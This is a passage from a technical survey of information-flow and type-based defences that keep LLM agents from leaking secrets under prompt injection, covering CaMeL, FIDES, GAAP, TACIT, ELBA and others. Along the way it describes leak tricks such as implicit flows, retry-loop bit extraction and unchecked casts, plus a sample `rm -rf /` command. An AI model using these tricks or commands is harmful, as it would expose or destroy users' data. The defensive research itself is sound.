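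Garby and colleagues also ran CaMeL themselves on the banking tasks. With GPT-5.2, it completed 32 of 48 runs without policy checks and 18 with them. It resisted every attack in the finished runs when the checks were on, but it also resisted all but 5 of 622 attacks across two models when they were off. This is because about two-thirds of the pairings of task and attack require a tool call that would never appear in a plan for the user's task. On this benchmark, planning before reading stops most attacks, while the label checks stop a few more but keep many tasks from being completed.

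Planning first helps less when the user asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions. In that case, CaMeL's planner wrote a program with a branch for each tool, so the file's contents still determined which tools the program called.

CaMeL's interpreter also leaks information. Garby and colleagues found that it raises a variable's label only on the branch that runs, so the trick with `found` and `tmp` works. The interpreter also runs inside an ordinary Python loop that retries after a failure. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, and the outer loop doesn't track that information, so a program written to exploit this could extract a whole secret one bit at a time.

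### When text enters a model's context

An interpreter can follow a value through a program, but not through a language model that reads it. Cai, Wen and Tang (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, argue that conventional tracking fails here. A model may summarise or translate what it reads, or use it only to choose the next action, leaving no copied string for a tracker to follow.

One reply is to label the model's whole context by default, which covers quotes, paraphrases and encodings alike. This is safe, but a single untrusted email makes every later action untrusted. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* measured how much this reduces task completion with GPT-4o, a 2024 model, and compared the approach with FIDES, which is designed to limit the loss. The table gives the percentage of AgentDojo tasks completed when there was no attack.

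| Tasks | No checks | Whole-context labels | FIDES |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0 | 37.0 | 59.0 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 41.0 |
| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 52.5 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 47.6 |

FIDES also labels the planner's whole context, but it keeps the label low by hiding data from the planner. When a tool returns something that would raise the label, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the planner only a name such as `#read_emails_0`. The planner can pass that name to another tool or have a quarantined model summarise the contents into a new variable. An attacker could still spoil the summary, for instance by making the quarantined model return an empty one, but could not redirect the planner.

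CaMeL's planner stops after writing its program, whereas the FIDES planner keeps choosing actions as results arrive. Sometimes its next action depends on what a variable contains, such as whether an email asks for a meeting. The planner can have the quarantined model answer only true or false, then read that answer. A policy may accept this one bit from an untrusted source because it is too small to hold instructions. If the planner reads the full email instead, the label of its context rises.

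With policy checks on, FIDES stopped every genuine attack in AgentDojo. GPT-4o often mishandled the variables, which explains much of the poor result on travel tasks. With OpenAI's o1 model, FIDES completed 68 percent of those tasks. The tests favored FIDES somewhat, because the researchers marked a field as untrusted if the benchmark contained an attack that used it, and nobody has such a list of attacks for real data. The researchers also hid data only when it was untrusted, so they did not test hiding data to keep it confidential.

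FIDES guarantees explicit secrecy, which is weaker than noninterference. This guarantee covers data that passes directly into a tool call, but not what an observer could infer from which calls the agent makes. The designers of FIDES considered full noninterference too restrictive because it would essentially forbid public actions after any secret read, much like Schneider's rule against sending.

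A more fine-grained way to handle lost labels is to estimate which messages influenced an answer, regenerate the answer from those messages alone, and give the new answer only their labels.

NeuroTaint, a system by Cai and colleagues, instead looks for the influence afterward, in the log of a finished run. For each sensitive tool call, it searches the arguments for a random marker that it planted in the untrusted text when a tool returned it. It then checks whether the arguments and the untrusted text share sequences of characters or contain passages with a similar meaning. If it finds nothing, it uses a language model to judge whether the agent would have made the same call if the untrusted text had been neutral. NeuroTaint saves its records between sessions, so it can connect a stored note with a report written days later.

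The researchers tested NeuroTaint on TaintBench, a set of 400 scenarios which they built on 20 agent frameworks. Untrusted text influenced a sensitive call in 200 of them. NeuroTaint found 187 of these and raised 16 false alarms, while a baseline modelled on FIDES found 108 and raised 106. These results show that a label on the whole context is poor evidence of what influenced a call. FIDES itself might still not have allowed the calls that the baseline missed, because such a label covers any paraphrase, at least within one session.

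In ten of the 13 cases NeuroTaint missed, repeated paraphrasing or a long delay had weakened the resemblance. A hostile model could weaken it deliberately, for example by packing a contract into one large integer, and Cai and colleagues exclude hidden encodings from their threat model. NeuroTaint also raises its alarm only after the email has been sent, so it is better suited to investigating past runs than to guarding secrets.

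### Keeping data from the model's provider

CaMeL and FIDES assume that the user trusts the planner's provider, which the contract company does not. *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* (Stanley, Verma and colleagues, 2026) also treats the provider as untrusted, for personal assistants that shop, book flights and send email. In its threat model, the adversary can read everything the model receives and control everything it produces.

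The GAAP system keeps private data in a database on the user's side. The model receives the names of the entries, such as "date of birth", but not the values. Users have to keep private data out of their prompts, so they ask "Given my age, am I eligible to vote?" without giving the age. The model then writes a plan in a small language that has only tool calls and `if` statements. GAAP's interpreter looks up the values, labels them and follows them through the plan.

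GAAP labels every instruction that depends on a condition, in both branches. If it blocks a call, the plan continues with a labelled error value, so an outsider cannot learn anything from the program stopping.

Each permission pairs one piece of data with one recipient. The first time a plan tries to send contract text to the broker, GAAP asks the user whether the contents of `2026.txt` may go to that address, and it stores the answer. The model's provider is also a recipient, so a plan can return a result to the model and request another plan only if the user lets the provider have the data used to produce that result. Every call in the new plan then carries the data's label. GAAP can therefore control the leak through `print(summary)`, which no sandbox can stop.

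Private data sent to an outside service can also come back. Suppose the agent gives an airline the user's passport number, and the user later asks it to forward the check-in confirmation to a friend. The confirmation may contain the number. GAAP logs each disclosure, so it labels the confirmation as possibly containing the number and checks whether the friend is allowed to see that number. Because this could label everything the airline returns, people can annotate each tool with the data it might repeat. An order confirmation, for example, might repeat the items ordered but not the customer's password.

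Stanley and colleagues tested seven attacks on each of 20 tasks, and none got private data out of GAAP. All seven worked against an unprotected agent on at least some tasks. Five got past a language model acting as judge, and five got past Conseca, which has an isolated model write a policy for each task. GAAP completed two fewer of the 20 tasks than the unprotected agent. It did about as well as the unprotected agent on AgentDojo and 10 percent worse on AgentDyn, a benchmark whose tasks often require unexpected steps. CaMeL, which cannot revise its plan, completes none of AgentDyn's tasks. The researchers had GAAP assume that the user approved every disclosure in both benchmarks, so those results show the effect of its planning language but not of its refusals.

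GAAP also cost 2.9 times as much to run as the unprotected agent across the two benchmarks, and took 188 seconds per task instead of 28. It asked the user 1.5 questions per task over a series of 100 tasks, compared with 3.8 when it could not reuse earlier answers. That is still enough to risk approval fatigue, and GAAP can reuse a careless answer in later tasks. GAAP protects only secrecy, so an injected instruction can still get the agent to delete a file or buy the wrong item if this discloses nothing new.

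### Agents that remember

Girrens and Wang built SPA for agents that keep results from one request to the next. SPA tracks both secrecy and trustworthiness. In their example, a user asks an agent on Monday to save the details of an invoice, which contains an attacker's account number. On Tuesday, the user asks the agent to pay it. If the agent stored the number without its label, a system that tracks labels only within one request has no basis for stopping the payment.

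SPA stores each result with its label and gives later planners only a description, such as the format of the data, its meaning and the request that produced it. A planner can refer to "Monday's invoice" in a new plan without reading it. SPA retrieves the stored value, with its original label, only when the plan runs.

SPA also checks the complete plan before any tool runs. Its planning language does not allow a variable to change, so the email to the broker would appear once in each branch of the `if`. SPA gives both calls the contract's label and rejects the plan. It uses only labels to do this, before it loads the contract, so the broker learns nothing from the refusal.

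Girrens and Wang tested SPA on AgentDojo and on their own version of it, which splits each task into two to five successive requests. They used GPT-5.4-nano, a small model.

| | Tasks completed without an attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Original tasks, label checks off | 53.0% | 0.4% |
| Original tasks, label checks on | 29.0% | 0.0% |
| Split tasks, label checks off | 62.5% | 0.3% |
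| Split tasks, label checks on | 35.3% | 0.2% |

The 0.2 percent includes two runs that AgentDojo counted as successful attacks although SPA had rejected the plan. On the original tasks, the checks stopped four attacks out of 949 and reduced completed tasks by 24 percentage points. Fixing the plan in advance had already stopped the rest, as it did with CaMeL. Girrens and Wang point out that the benchmark's attack rarely involves the delayed kind of harm that SPA is meant to prevent, so the test probably understates how much the checks help. It does not overstate the loss of completed tasks, because most of the rejected plans used outside data in an important action, as an agent must to pay a genuine invoice.

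Developers have been slow to adopt these methods. In *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI*, Kim, Liu and colleagues (2026) examined six open-source agents, including versions of Codex and Google's Gemini CLI, and found that none tracked information flow. They cite slow execution and the spread of labels as the main obstacles.

### A proof for programs that do not exist yet

An interpreter could score well on AgentDojo and still have leaks like those in CaMeL's interpreter, because only a program designed to exploit them would expose them. Garby and colleagues therefore set out to prove that an interpreter has no such leaks. They designed LLMbda, a small language for writing agents, and proved a form of noninterference for it in Lean, a programming language for writing proofs that a computer can check. The theorem covers every LLMbda program, including those a model writes while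 the agent is running.

An LLMbda program can prompt a model, temporarily copy the conversation, or clear it. It can therefore build the dual-LLM pattern by having the model read an email in a cleared copy of the conversation and then discarding that copy. Each conversation has a single label that covers everything sent so far. The model's answer takes this label, and so does the result of any code in the answer. The proof therefore needs no assumptions about how a model uses what it reads, which confirms that labelling the whole context is safe.

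LLMbda mostly avoids the problem of the skipped assignment because its variables cannot change. An `if` produces a value, and that value takes the condition's label whichever branch runs. Conversations can change, so LLMbda stops a program that tries to add to a public conversation inside a confidential branch.

Models answer with some randomness, so the theorem compares probabilities. Suppose a program runs with one secret and then with another, and let `μ(r)` and `ν(r)` be the probabilities that an outsider sees the result `r`. Each set of probabilities may add up to less than 1, because the program may never finish. The theorem states that some third set, `ω`, satisfies

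```
μ(r) ≤ ω(r)  and  ν(r) ≤ ω(r)  for every r,   with  sum of ω(r) ≤ 1
```

If the program always finishes, `μ` and `ν` each add up to 1, so both must equal `ω` and the outsider learns nothing about the secret. Otherwise, the secret can affect whether the program finishes, and a stop for breaking a policy counts as not finishing. Garby and colleagues also proved a limit on this leak:

```
½ × sum of |μ(r) − ν(r)|  ≤  average probability of not finishing
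```

For example, if the program fails to finish in 2 percent of runs with one secret and 4 percent with the other, the left side is at most 0.03. The limit applies to one run, so a script outside LLMbda that restarted the program after every stop could bring back the leak in CaMeL's retry loop.

The theorem also depends on people labelling the data sources correctly and putting a check in front of every sensitive tool. It treats the sources and tools as part of the LLMbda program. The proof does not cover the code that contacts the model over the network, or count the model's provider as an observer. A program can put secret text into a conversation, which raises the conversation's label but still sends the text to the provider. To keep that text from the provider, the contract company would have to run the model itself or add a check before each prompt.

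Because strict labels block so much useful work, LLMbda lets a program endorse a value, that is, mark untrusted data as trusted. A second theorem guarantees that endorsement cannot release secrets, even if an attacker chooses all the untrusted data. Endorsement can still let an attacker influence what the agent does.

Garby and colleagues used LLMbda to build an agent called Randori, which first runs its program on simulated data. It can correct mistakes there without picking up labels from real data or repeating real payments. With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 36 of the 48 banking runs, twice as many as CaMeL with its checks on, but the uncertainty is large because there were only 16 different tasks. Across three models, 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to follow the payment instructions in a file, and the agent's program had endorsed the altered file.

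Some of Randori's advantage comes from these exceptions. Without endorsement, it resisted every attack on the two models tested, but one model completed 30 runs instead of 36 and the other 26 instead of 31. The planner must choose its endorsements before it reads any untrusted data, but LLMbda does not by itself stop the planner from endorsing too much.

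## Can a type checker keep code pure and secrets sealed?

A type checker, like SPA's check of a complete plan, examines a program before the program reads any data, so a rejection reveals nothing about the contracts.

Odersky and colleagues built TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types) on this principle. The agent writes its programs in Scala 3, whose compiler determines a type for every value, such as `String` for text or `Int` for a whole number. With an experimental feature called capture checking, a value's type also lists the capabilities the value can use. If a program would use a capability where the types forbid it, the compiler rejects the whole program, so none of it runs.

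### From the model to the compiler

TACIT runs as an MCP server, so agents such as Claude Code can use it without modification. The model sends Scala code in a tool call, and the compiler checks it. If the check fails, the model receives the error message and can try again. If it succeeds, the program runs and TACIT returns the output to the model. The program can reach files, commands and the network only through TACIT's library.

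The trusted parts of the design are the compiler, the library, the software that runs the compiled code, and a local model that may read the contracts. The cloud model and any code it writes are untrusted.

TACIT does not control the agent's other tools. If the agent still had Claude Code's shell, it could print a contract with `cat 2026.txt`. The project's documentation (lampepfl, *TACIT*) therefore recommends turning off the agent's built-in file, shell and network tools.

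### Types that list capabilities

Capture checking distinguishes functions by what they can use:

| Type | What the function can use |
|---|---|
| `String -> Int` | No capabilities, so it is pure |
| `String ->{conn} Int` | Only the capability `conn` |
| `String => Int` | Any capability |

The compiler can usually infer these lists, so the model rarely has to write them. Here are the two versions of `count` from the discussion of system calls, rewritten in Scala. (In code, `=>` separates a function's parameters from its body. Only in a type does it mean that the function may use any capability.)

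```
val count1 = (text: String) => text.split(" ").length

val count2 = (text: String) =>
  conn.send("done")
  text.split(" ").length
```

The type of `count1` is `String -> Int`. Because `count2` uses the connection, its type is `String ->{conn} Int`, and the compiler rejects it wherever a program requires a pure function. The kernel could not identify which function had sent the message, but the types show which one uses the connection before either function runs.

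The agent cannot hide the `send` in a helper function. The helper's type would list `conn`, and so would the type of any function that called the helper. Objects work the same way, so a logger that holds an open file has that file listed in its type.

### Two programs on a sealed contract

TACIT returns the text of a confidential file in a container called `Classified`. An agent's program works on the contents mainly through the container's `map` method:

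```
trait Classified[+T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

`T` and `U` stand for any types. `map` applies a function to the hidden value and puts the result in a new container. The thin arrow means the function must be pure. The paper's design also has a `reveal` method that returns the hidden value, but calling it requires a capability the agent does not have.

This program counts the words in a contract, and it compiles:

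```
val contract = readClassified("2026.txt")
val words = contract.map(text => text.split(" ").length)
```

The type of `contract` is `Classified[String]`, and the type of `words` is `Classified[Int]`. The next program tries to copy the contract into an ordinary file:

```
val out = access("notes.txt")
contract.map(text => out.write(text))
```

`access` returns a file handle, which is a capability. The function uses `out`, so the compiler adds `out` to the function's type and then reports a mismatch (`Unit` means that the function returns no useful value):

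```
Found:    (text: String) ->{out} Unit
Required: String -> Unit
```

The program never starts, so it cannot write even part of the contract. Replacing `out.write` with `println` would also fail, because printing requires a capability too.

The result must stay in a container because a pure function can return the secret, as `same` did. `contract.map(text => text)` compiles, but it only produces another sealed value. If the program prints that value, the model receives `Classified(****)`. But harmless results stay sealed too, so the model cannot read the word count or use it to decide what to do next.

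The container also blocks implicit flows. The line `if contract.contains("penalty")` does not compile, because the container has no `contains` method. A function inside `map` can test for the word, but it cannot record the answer in an outside variable, because capture checking treats writing to that variable as a side effect. This rules out both the trick with `found` and `tmp` and the shared list `notes` that the kernel could not monitor.

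TACIT can tell Program A from Program B, which no monitor of system calls can do. Its type checker accepts a program that reads the key and then sends the constant `0`, because the constant is not sealed, but rejects one that sends the key's last bit, because that bit exists only inside a container. The type checker also rejects some harmless programs, such as one that sends the constant `0` from inside `map`.

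### Errors inside the container

An error message could also carry text out of the container. In Python, the error from `float("4.2m")` includes the string it failed to convert, and in Scala an exception from `contract.map(text => text.toDouble)` could expose text the same way.

Exceptions are side effects, but the types do not track them. According to Scala's *Safe Mode* reference page, tracking them would be impractical because so many ordinary events cause exceptions, including division by zero and running out of memory. TACIT instead catches exceptions while the program runs and turns them into failure values, which it can seal like any other result.

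This protects the contract but makes mistakes hard to find. In one test, Odersky and colleagues had to warn the model that if an exception occurred inside `map`, the program would appear to succeed but show the user nothing. They told it to return a message such as "No matching transaction" instead.

### Permissions that end with a block

A program that needs files calls `requestFileSystem`, which creates a capability for one folder, runs a block of code with it and then invalidates it. Suppose an agent tries to keep its access by returning a function that will read a file later:

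```
val reader = requestFileSystem("/project") {
  () => access("/project/prices.txt").read()
}
reader()
```

The function's type lists the folder's capability, which exists only inside the block. `reader` is outside the block, so its type cannot refer to that capability, and the compiler rejects the program. A sealed summary can leave the block because it does not give access to anything.

TACIT also needs checks at run time. The compiler cannot determine whether a computed path will lie inside the permitted folder, so the library checks each path when the program uses it. The library also compares host names and commands with allowlists. Calling `requestFileSystem` requires a capability, so a function inside `map` cannot use it to access files.

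### What safe mode forbids

Some features of ordinary Scala could make the compiler lose track of capabilities. One is the type cast, which tells the compiler to treat a value as if it had a different type. If `save` is a function that writes to a file, an agent could use a cast to pass it off as pure:

```
contract.map(save.asInstanceOf[String -> Unit])
```

Safe mode is a restricted version of Scala that forbids unchecked casts, annotations that turn off checks, and reflection, which lets a running program look up functions by name.

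Libraries pose a similar problem because Java's standard functions for writing files do not require a TACIT capability, so a function that used them would look pure. A program in safe mode can therefore use global functions and objects only if their developer compiled them in safe mode or marked them `@assumeSafe`. Agents cannot apply this mark to their own code because, as the software company VirtusLab points out, they could use it to get around the rules.

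The compiler does not verify that code marked `@assumeSafe` is safe. Scala's reference page gives the example of a function that caches its results. Caching changes memory, but nobody can observe the change if the underlying computation is pure, and the programmer has to confirm that it is. If a programmer applied the mark to a function that sends data but requires no capability, the compiler would treat the function as pure, and code inside `map` could call it.

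Odersky and colleagues estimate that the reusable part of the library takes about 1,000 lines of Scala. Each new set of tools also needs typed descriptions. For simulated airline and retail services, these took a few hundred lines per service.

### The finished contract program

Suppose the company marks the folder `/contracts` as confidential and adds a pure function called `diff` to the library. The cloud model can then write the whole program:

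```
requestFileSystem("/contracts") {
  val before = readClassified("/contracts/2025.txt")
  val after = readClassified("/contracts/2026.txt")
  val changes = before.flatMap(a => after.map(b => diff(a, b)))
  val summary = chat(changes.map(c => s"Summarise the changes: $c"))
  writeClassified("/contracts/summary.txt", summary)
  println(summary)
  println("finished")
}
```

`flatMap` works like `map` but takes a function that already returns a container, which avoids putting one container inside another. `chat` sends the changes to the trusted local model and seals the reply. `writeClassified` can write only to confidential files, so it cannot copy the summary to an ordinary folder.

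TACIT has two output channels. The normal channel goes back to the cloud model, which receives `Classified(****)` followed by `finished`. The secure channel goes only to the user, who sees the actual summary. The line `print(summary)`, which leaked the text in the Python version, is therefore safe here. If the user then asks how long the summary is, the model can run `println(summary.map(_.length))`, which shows the user the number but returns only asterisks to the model.

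The `chat` function contacts another model, but the type system treats it as pure. This is safe only if the company trusts that model and the service does not reuse the text in later requests. According to Glama's *TACIT*, a copy of the project's newer documentation, `chat` works with any service with an OpenAI-compatible interface, so a wrong setting could send the contracts to a cloud provider.

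Wording in a contract could still influence the local model, for example by getting it to leave a change out of the summary, but it could not trigger a new action, because the local model has no tools and the cloud model never reads the contract.

### The safety test

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a sample software project with a folder of secrets, including API keys and confidential documents. They wrote 12 legitimate tasks, some of which required using the secrets, such as summarising a confidential incident report. They combined each task with 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials. Some injections were simple notes in the project, while others imitated system messages or supplied Scala code for reading the secrets.

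In another 11 trials, the user was the attacker. The user asked for secrets directly in five of them and used social engineering in the other six, such as claiming to be an administrator in an emergency. The researchers ran all 131 trials with two models, once with the secrets in `Classified` containers and once with them as ordinary text. A trial counted as a leak if a secret appeared in the agent's output.

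| | Sonnet 4.6, sealed | Sonnet 4.6, ordinary text | MiniMax M2.5, sealed | MiniMax M2.5, ordinary text |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Leaks in 120 injection trials | 0 | 0 | 0 | 3 |
| Leaks in 11 malicious requests | 0 | 2 | 0 | 8 |
| All trials without a leak | 100% | 98.5% | 100% | 91.6% |
| Legitimate tasks completed | 99.2% | 83.3% | 90.0% | 88.3% |

Without containers, safety depended on how well the model resisted manipulation. Claude Sonnet 4.6 resisted every injection and every direct request, and both of its leaks came from social engineering. MiniMax M2.5 leaked secrets in most of the malicious trials. This difference is hard to see in the overall percentages because 120 of the 131 trials were injections, which rarely worked on either model.

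Sealing the secrets did not reduce the number of completed tasks. Sonnet completed more with them sealed, but Odersky and colleagues suspect that this was partly an artefact of the test. With ordinary text, Sonnet often ran out of time or turns, and it sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection.

Eleven malicious requests are too few to establish a low leak rate on their own. Even if the true rate were 24 percent, 11 trials would produce no leaks about 5 percent of the time. The type rule is stronger evidence because it applies to every program the agent submits. The trials mainly confirm that the software applied this rule to the kinds of programs the two models wrote. They did not include a systematic search for programs that exploit a flaw in the compiler, so they could have missed such a flaw.

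### Can models do ordinary work in Scala?

A safe language is of little use if models cannot write it, and capture checking is too new to appear often in their training data. Odersky and colleagues therefore compared TACIT with ordinary tool calls on τ²-bench, in which an agent handles requests from simulated customers. They ran each task ten times, and the table shows the percentage of tasks solved.

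| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, TACIT | Retail, tool calls | Retail, TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8 | 45.2 | 53.3 | 57.0 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4 | 61.0 | 75.1 | 77.5 |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8 | 58.6 | 74.6 | 75.5 |

TACIT did slightly better in all six comparisons. The researchers credit its typed results, which are clearer than raw JSON, and the compiler's error messages. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues, MiniMax M2.5 resolved 41.7 percent with TACIT and 43.3 percent with tool calls, a difference of five issues. The researchers think TACIT did worse there because coding agents rely on shell commands that are awkward to express through its library.

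The compiler rejected few programs on τ²-bench. Depending on the model and the type of customer service, between 0.32 and 7.93 percent of programs needed another attempt, and those needed 1.06 to 1.39 retries on average. Many of the recurring errors were unrelated to security, such as misusing the dollar sign, which has a special meaning inside some Scala strings.

Checking a typical program takes less than a second, much less time than the wait for the model. *What's in the Box* (2025) reports that capture checking took less than 15 percent of the time needed to compile Scala's standard library.

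These benchmarks test whether models can write Scala, but they do not measure how much useful work sealing stops an agent from doing. The customer-service tools returned ordinary values, so the model could read a reservation and decide what to do next. VirtusLab warns that classifying too much would make an agent far less useful, because much of its value comes from reading files, emails and web pages.

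### AgentDojo and the comparison with CaMeL

AgentDojo is a better test of that drawback, because TACIT's version of it seals most of the data that could contain an attack. Odersky and colleagues used the same two models as the CaMeL paper and took CaMeL's results from it. The table gives the percentage of tasks completed.

| Tasks | Gemini 2.5 Pro, CaMeL | Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT | o4-mini-high, CaMeL | o4-mini-high, TACIT |
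|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 52.8 | 56.9 | 62.5 | 59.0 |
| Office | 53.8 | 50.5 | 81.4 | 52.9 |
| Slack | 48.6 | 40.0 | 68.6 | 47.6 |
| Travel | 1.4 | 64.3 | 74.3 | 68.6 |

Odersky and colleagues call the two systems' results comparable, which is generous to TACIT. With o4-mini-high, CaMeL completed more tasks in all four groups and led by 28.5 percentage points on office tasks. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT had a large advantage only in travel, where CaMeL's quoted score was 1.4 percent (2 of 140 trials). CaMeL completed 74.3 percent of the same travel tasks with o4-mini-high, so the low score probably reflects a problem specific to the Gemini run and should not count as evidence against CaMeL's design.

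Across the two models, one of about 1,900 attacks against TACIT counted as successful. This was a scoring error like the one in CaMeL's evaluation, because the agent booked the right hotel but quoted a review that recommended another. The quoted CaMeL results for the same two models include one successful attack, in banking.

It is unclear how much of this security came from local purity. The model's instructions for the AgentDojo test stated that side effects inside `map` would run immediately, and the published signature of `sendMoney` does not require a capability. The test version may therefore have let an agent make payments based on sealed text, which the stricter contract design would forbid. If so, much of the protection would have come from keeping the attacker's text away from the planner, as it did with CaMeL.

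CaMeL's planner also has to write in a small subset of Python. It cannot define its own functions, because the interpreter has to follow every value through the whole program. TACIT can check each function separately against its type, so agents can define functions, pass them to one another and use recursion. A TACIT agent can also read public results and use them to choose its next step, which CaMeL's planner cannot do.

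Odersky and colleagues add that CaMeL loses its labels once text enters a model's context, whereas TACIT never puts sealed text into the cloud model's context. This is an advantage over CaMeL, but FIDES, LLMbda and GAAP have their own ways to avoid the loss.

### How strong is the guarantee?

TACIT is secure only if a function with an empty list of capabilities has no side effects. Researchers have proved that the core rules of capture checking are sound, which means that a program that passes the check uses only the capabilities its types allow. *What's in the Box* includes one such proof, checked in Lean. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) also uses Lean to prove type and effect safety for an extension that sorts capabilities into kinds.

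These proofs cover small mathematical models of the language, not the compiler's code or the standard library functions that safe mode allows. Odersky and colleagues state that proving safe mode provides its intended guarantees would require a further semantic soundness argument.

A semantic proof defines what a type guarantees about a program's behaviour, however the programmer wrote the code. Someone could use that definition to prove that a function marked `@assumeSafe` behaves safely even if it breaks the compiler's rules internally. The RustBelt project has shown that this is possible for a similar boundary in Rust.

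*System Capybara* (Xu, Bračevac and colleagues, 2026) has since given a semantic proof for an extended core of capture checking, again in Lean. The proof shows that a well-typed program can read, write or use up only the memory locations its types allow, and that computations with read-only access do not change anything. This brings the theory closer to what TACIT needs, but the proof does not cover safe mode or establish noninterference for TACIT as a whole. Garby and colleagues proved noninterference for LLMbda, a much smaller language.

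The software is also still changing. Scala introduced safe mode as an experimental feature in version 3.8.3. According to TACIT's documentation in March 2026, the tool instead used a separate validator that searched the agent's code for forbidden patterns. A list of patterns may miss an unsafe feature that nobody thought to include, so it is weaker evidence of safety than a restriction built into the compiler. The newer documentation describes a setting that turns on the compiler's safe mode, but is inconsistent about whether it is on by default, so setting it explicitly is safer for users who rely on it.

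### Later versions

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) extends the approach to let agents call models from inside their programs. A program can contain a request such as `agent[Int]("count the late payments")`. When the program reaches this line, a model writes code for it, and the compiler checks that the code returns a whole number and uses only the capabilities available at that point.

In the contract example, the program could make such a request to the local model from inside `map`. The local model would read the contract and write code suited to its contents, whereas in TACIT the cloud model has to write all the code without seeing the text. The compiler would still require the new code to be pure.

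This flexibility made the coding harder. On 392 τ²-bench tasks, DeepSeek-V4-Flash solved 76.0 percent with LACUNA and 90.0 percent with ordinary tool calls. Zhao and colleagues describe these results as on par despite the 14-point gap. The compiler rejected 22.4 percent of the model's programs on the retail tasks, and 89 percent of those written by a weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, on the telecom tasks. So TACIT's low retry rates may not carry over to designs that require models to write more complex typed code.

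Eight AgentDojo attacks also succeeded against LACUNA across two models, compared with one against TACIT. Zhao and colleagues note that the type system cannot stop an attacker from steering a model into misusing a capability the task requires.

TACIT's developers have also released ATC, a terminal coding agent with TACIT built in. It denies access by default and can grant permissions temporarily or for one session. Scala Days' *Making the AI agents safe with Scala* describes another agent, CapybaraClaw, which applies the same methods to assistants that run permanently.

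According to Glama, TACIT now lets a program use a sealed API key to log in to an approved service without revealing the key to the model. A program can also send a sealed document to an approved service and receive a sealed reply. These features make more tasks possible, but every host on the allowlist may now receive secrets. An agent might upload a contract to an attacker's account on such a host, as in the leaks through Anthropic's file service.

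The containers also do not protect files from damage. A program can seal any text and use `writeClassified` to overwrite a contract with it. Administrators can block all writes to confidential files, but then the contract program could not save its summary in the confidential folder, and the user would have to read it on the secure channel.

A `Classified` container marks a value as confidential but does not record whose it is. If a company kept two customers' contracts in separate confidential folders and gave an agent access to both, the agent's program could copy one customer's contract into the other's folder and still pass the type check.

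## What changes when the whole agent application is typed?

TACIT type-checks the code that a model writes, but not the harness, the separate software that calls the model, retries after errors and starts sub-agents. Leaks can begin in the harness, as they can in CaMeL's retry loop. Zhou and colleagues therefore propose language-based agent control, in which developers write the surrounding application in the same typed language as the agent's programs, so one type checker covers both. Their system, ELBA, uses Haskell, whose types separate pure functions from code with side effects.

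### The calculator

In ELBA, a call to an agent is an ordinary function:

```
agent :: Defs -> Prompt -> t
```

The symbol `::` introduces a type. `Defs` lists the functions that the agent's code may use, `Prompt` is the text of the request, and `t` stands for whatever type the surrounding program requires. When the program reaches the call, ELBA sends the model the prompt, the available functions and the required type. The model writes a Haskell expression, and the compiler checks that it has this type. If it doesn't, the model receives the error message and tries again. If it does, ELBA runs the code, and the result becomes the value of the call.

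The calculator agent from the discussion of pure functions could look like this:

```
calculate :: String -> Int
calculate question = agent mathTools question
```

If the model obeyed the visitor who wanted the server's files deleted first, it might write:

```
do system "rm -rf /"
   return (factorial 5)
```

The function `system` runs a shell command, so its type contains the marker `IO`, for input and output. Any code that runs an `IO` action also has an `IO` type, which makes this program an `IO Int`. The calculator requires a plain `Int`, so the compiler rejects the program before it deletes anything, without the developer having to list any dangerous commands.

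Ordinary Haskell has loopholes that would defeat this check. The function `unsafePerformIO`, of type `IO a -> a`, makes any action look like a pure value, and Template Haskell can reach parts of a library that its author has hidden. GHC's *Safe Haskell*, a chapter in the manual of the main Haskell compiler, describes a restricted mode that forbids both. As in Scala's safe mode, some library code is exempt because its author vouches for it, and an optional setting limits this exemption to packages the operator has approved. The mode does not protect the computer during compilation, when a custom preprocessor can start any program, so the operator also has to control the compiler's options.

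As with LLMbda, the guarantee does not cover data sent to the model's provider. If the model runs in the cloud, `agent` sends its prompt to the provider, but a function that passes a contract to `agent` and gets back an `Int` still counts as pure.

### The bibliography

A second example is the earlier rule that every entry an agent adds to a bibliography must come from DBLP, a trusted database of computer science publications. The developer could enforce it by offering only a single tool that fetches a record and appends it in one step. That would prevent invented entries, but the agent could no longer use code to sort or filter the records first, and the model would have to read them one by one.

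ELBA allows such code and still enforces the rule. The developer writes a small library with roughly these types:

```
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

A DOI is a permanent identifier for a publication. `BibIO` marks code whose only side effects come from this library, and `()` means that a function returns no useful value. The developer then calls the agent with the required type `BibIO ()`. The model might write the following program, in which `earliest` stands for pure code that picks the oldest record:

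```
do dois <- dblpSearch "noninterference"
   records <- mapM dblpFetchBib dois
   appendToBibFile (earliest records)
```

Two features of the types enforce the rule. The library hides the function that creates a `Trusted` value, so the agent can get one only by fetching a record from DBLP. Haskell's standard `writeFile` has an `IO` type, which does not type-check in a `BibIO` program, so the agent cannot write to the file in any other way. The agent can still choose an irrelevant paper, because the types guarantee only where a record came from.

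Zhou and colleagues tested this agent on 100 requests for citations on a computer science topic. None of its 925 citations had a wrong author, year or DOI, compared with 19 of the 1,002 from an ordinary agent using the same model, Claude Sonnet 5. That agent had a web search tool and wrote the citations itself, so some of the improvement may have come from using a good database. The ordinary agent also made about four times as many model calls and used 65 times as many input tokens, because the model had to read the search results.

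`BibIO` restricts which operations the agent can perform but not their order. *Concordat* (2026) restricts the order too, by making the available tools depend on the state of a conversation. For example, an airline's agent could cancel a booking only after the customer had agreed. *ETAS* (2026) designs a new language whose types describe the side effects of an entire multi-agent system.

### Sub-agents inherit the limits

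An `agent` call produces one complete program, but an agent often needs to look at a result before it decides what to do next. In ELBA, the program does this by calling `agent` again with the result in the prompt:

```
do dois <- dblpSearch "noninterference"
   record <- dblpFetchBib (head dois)
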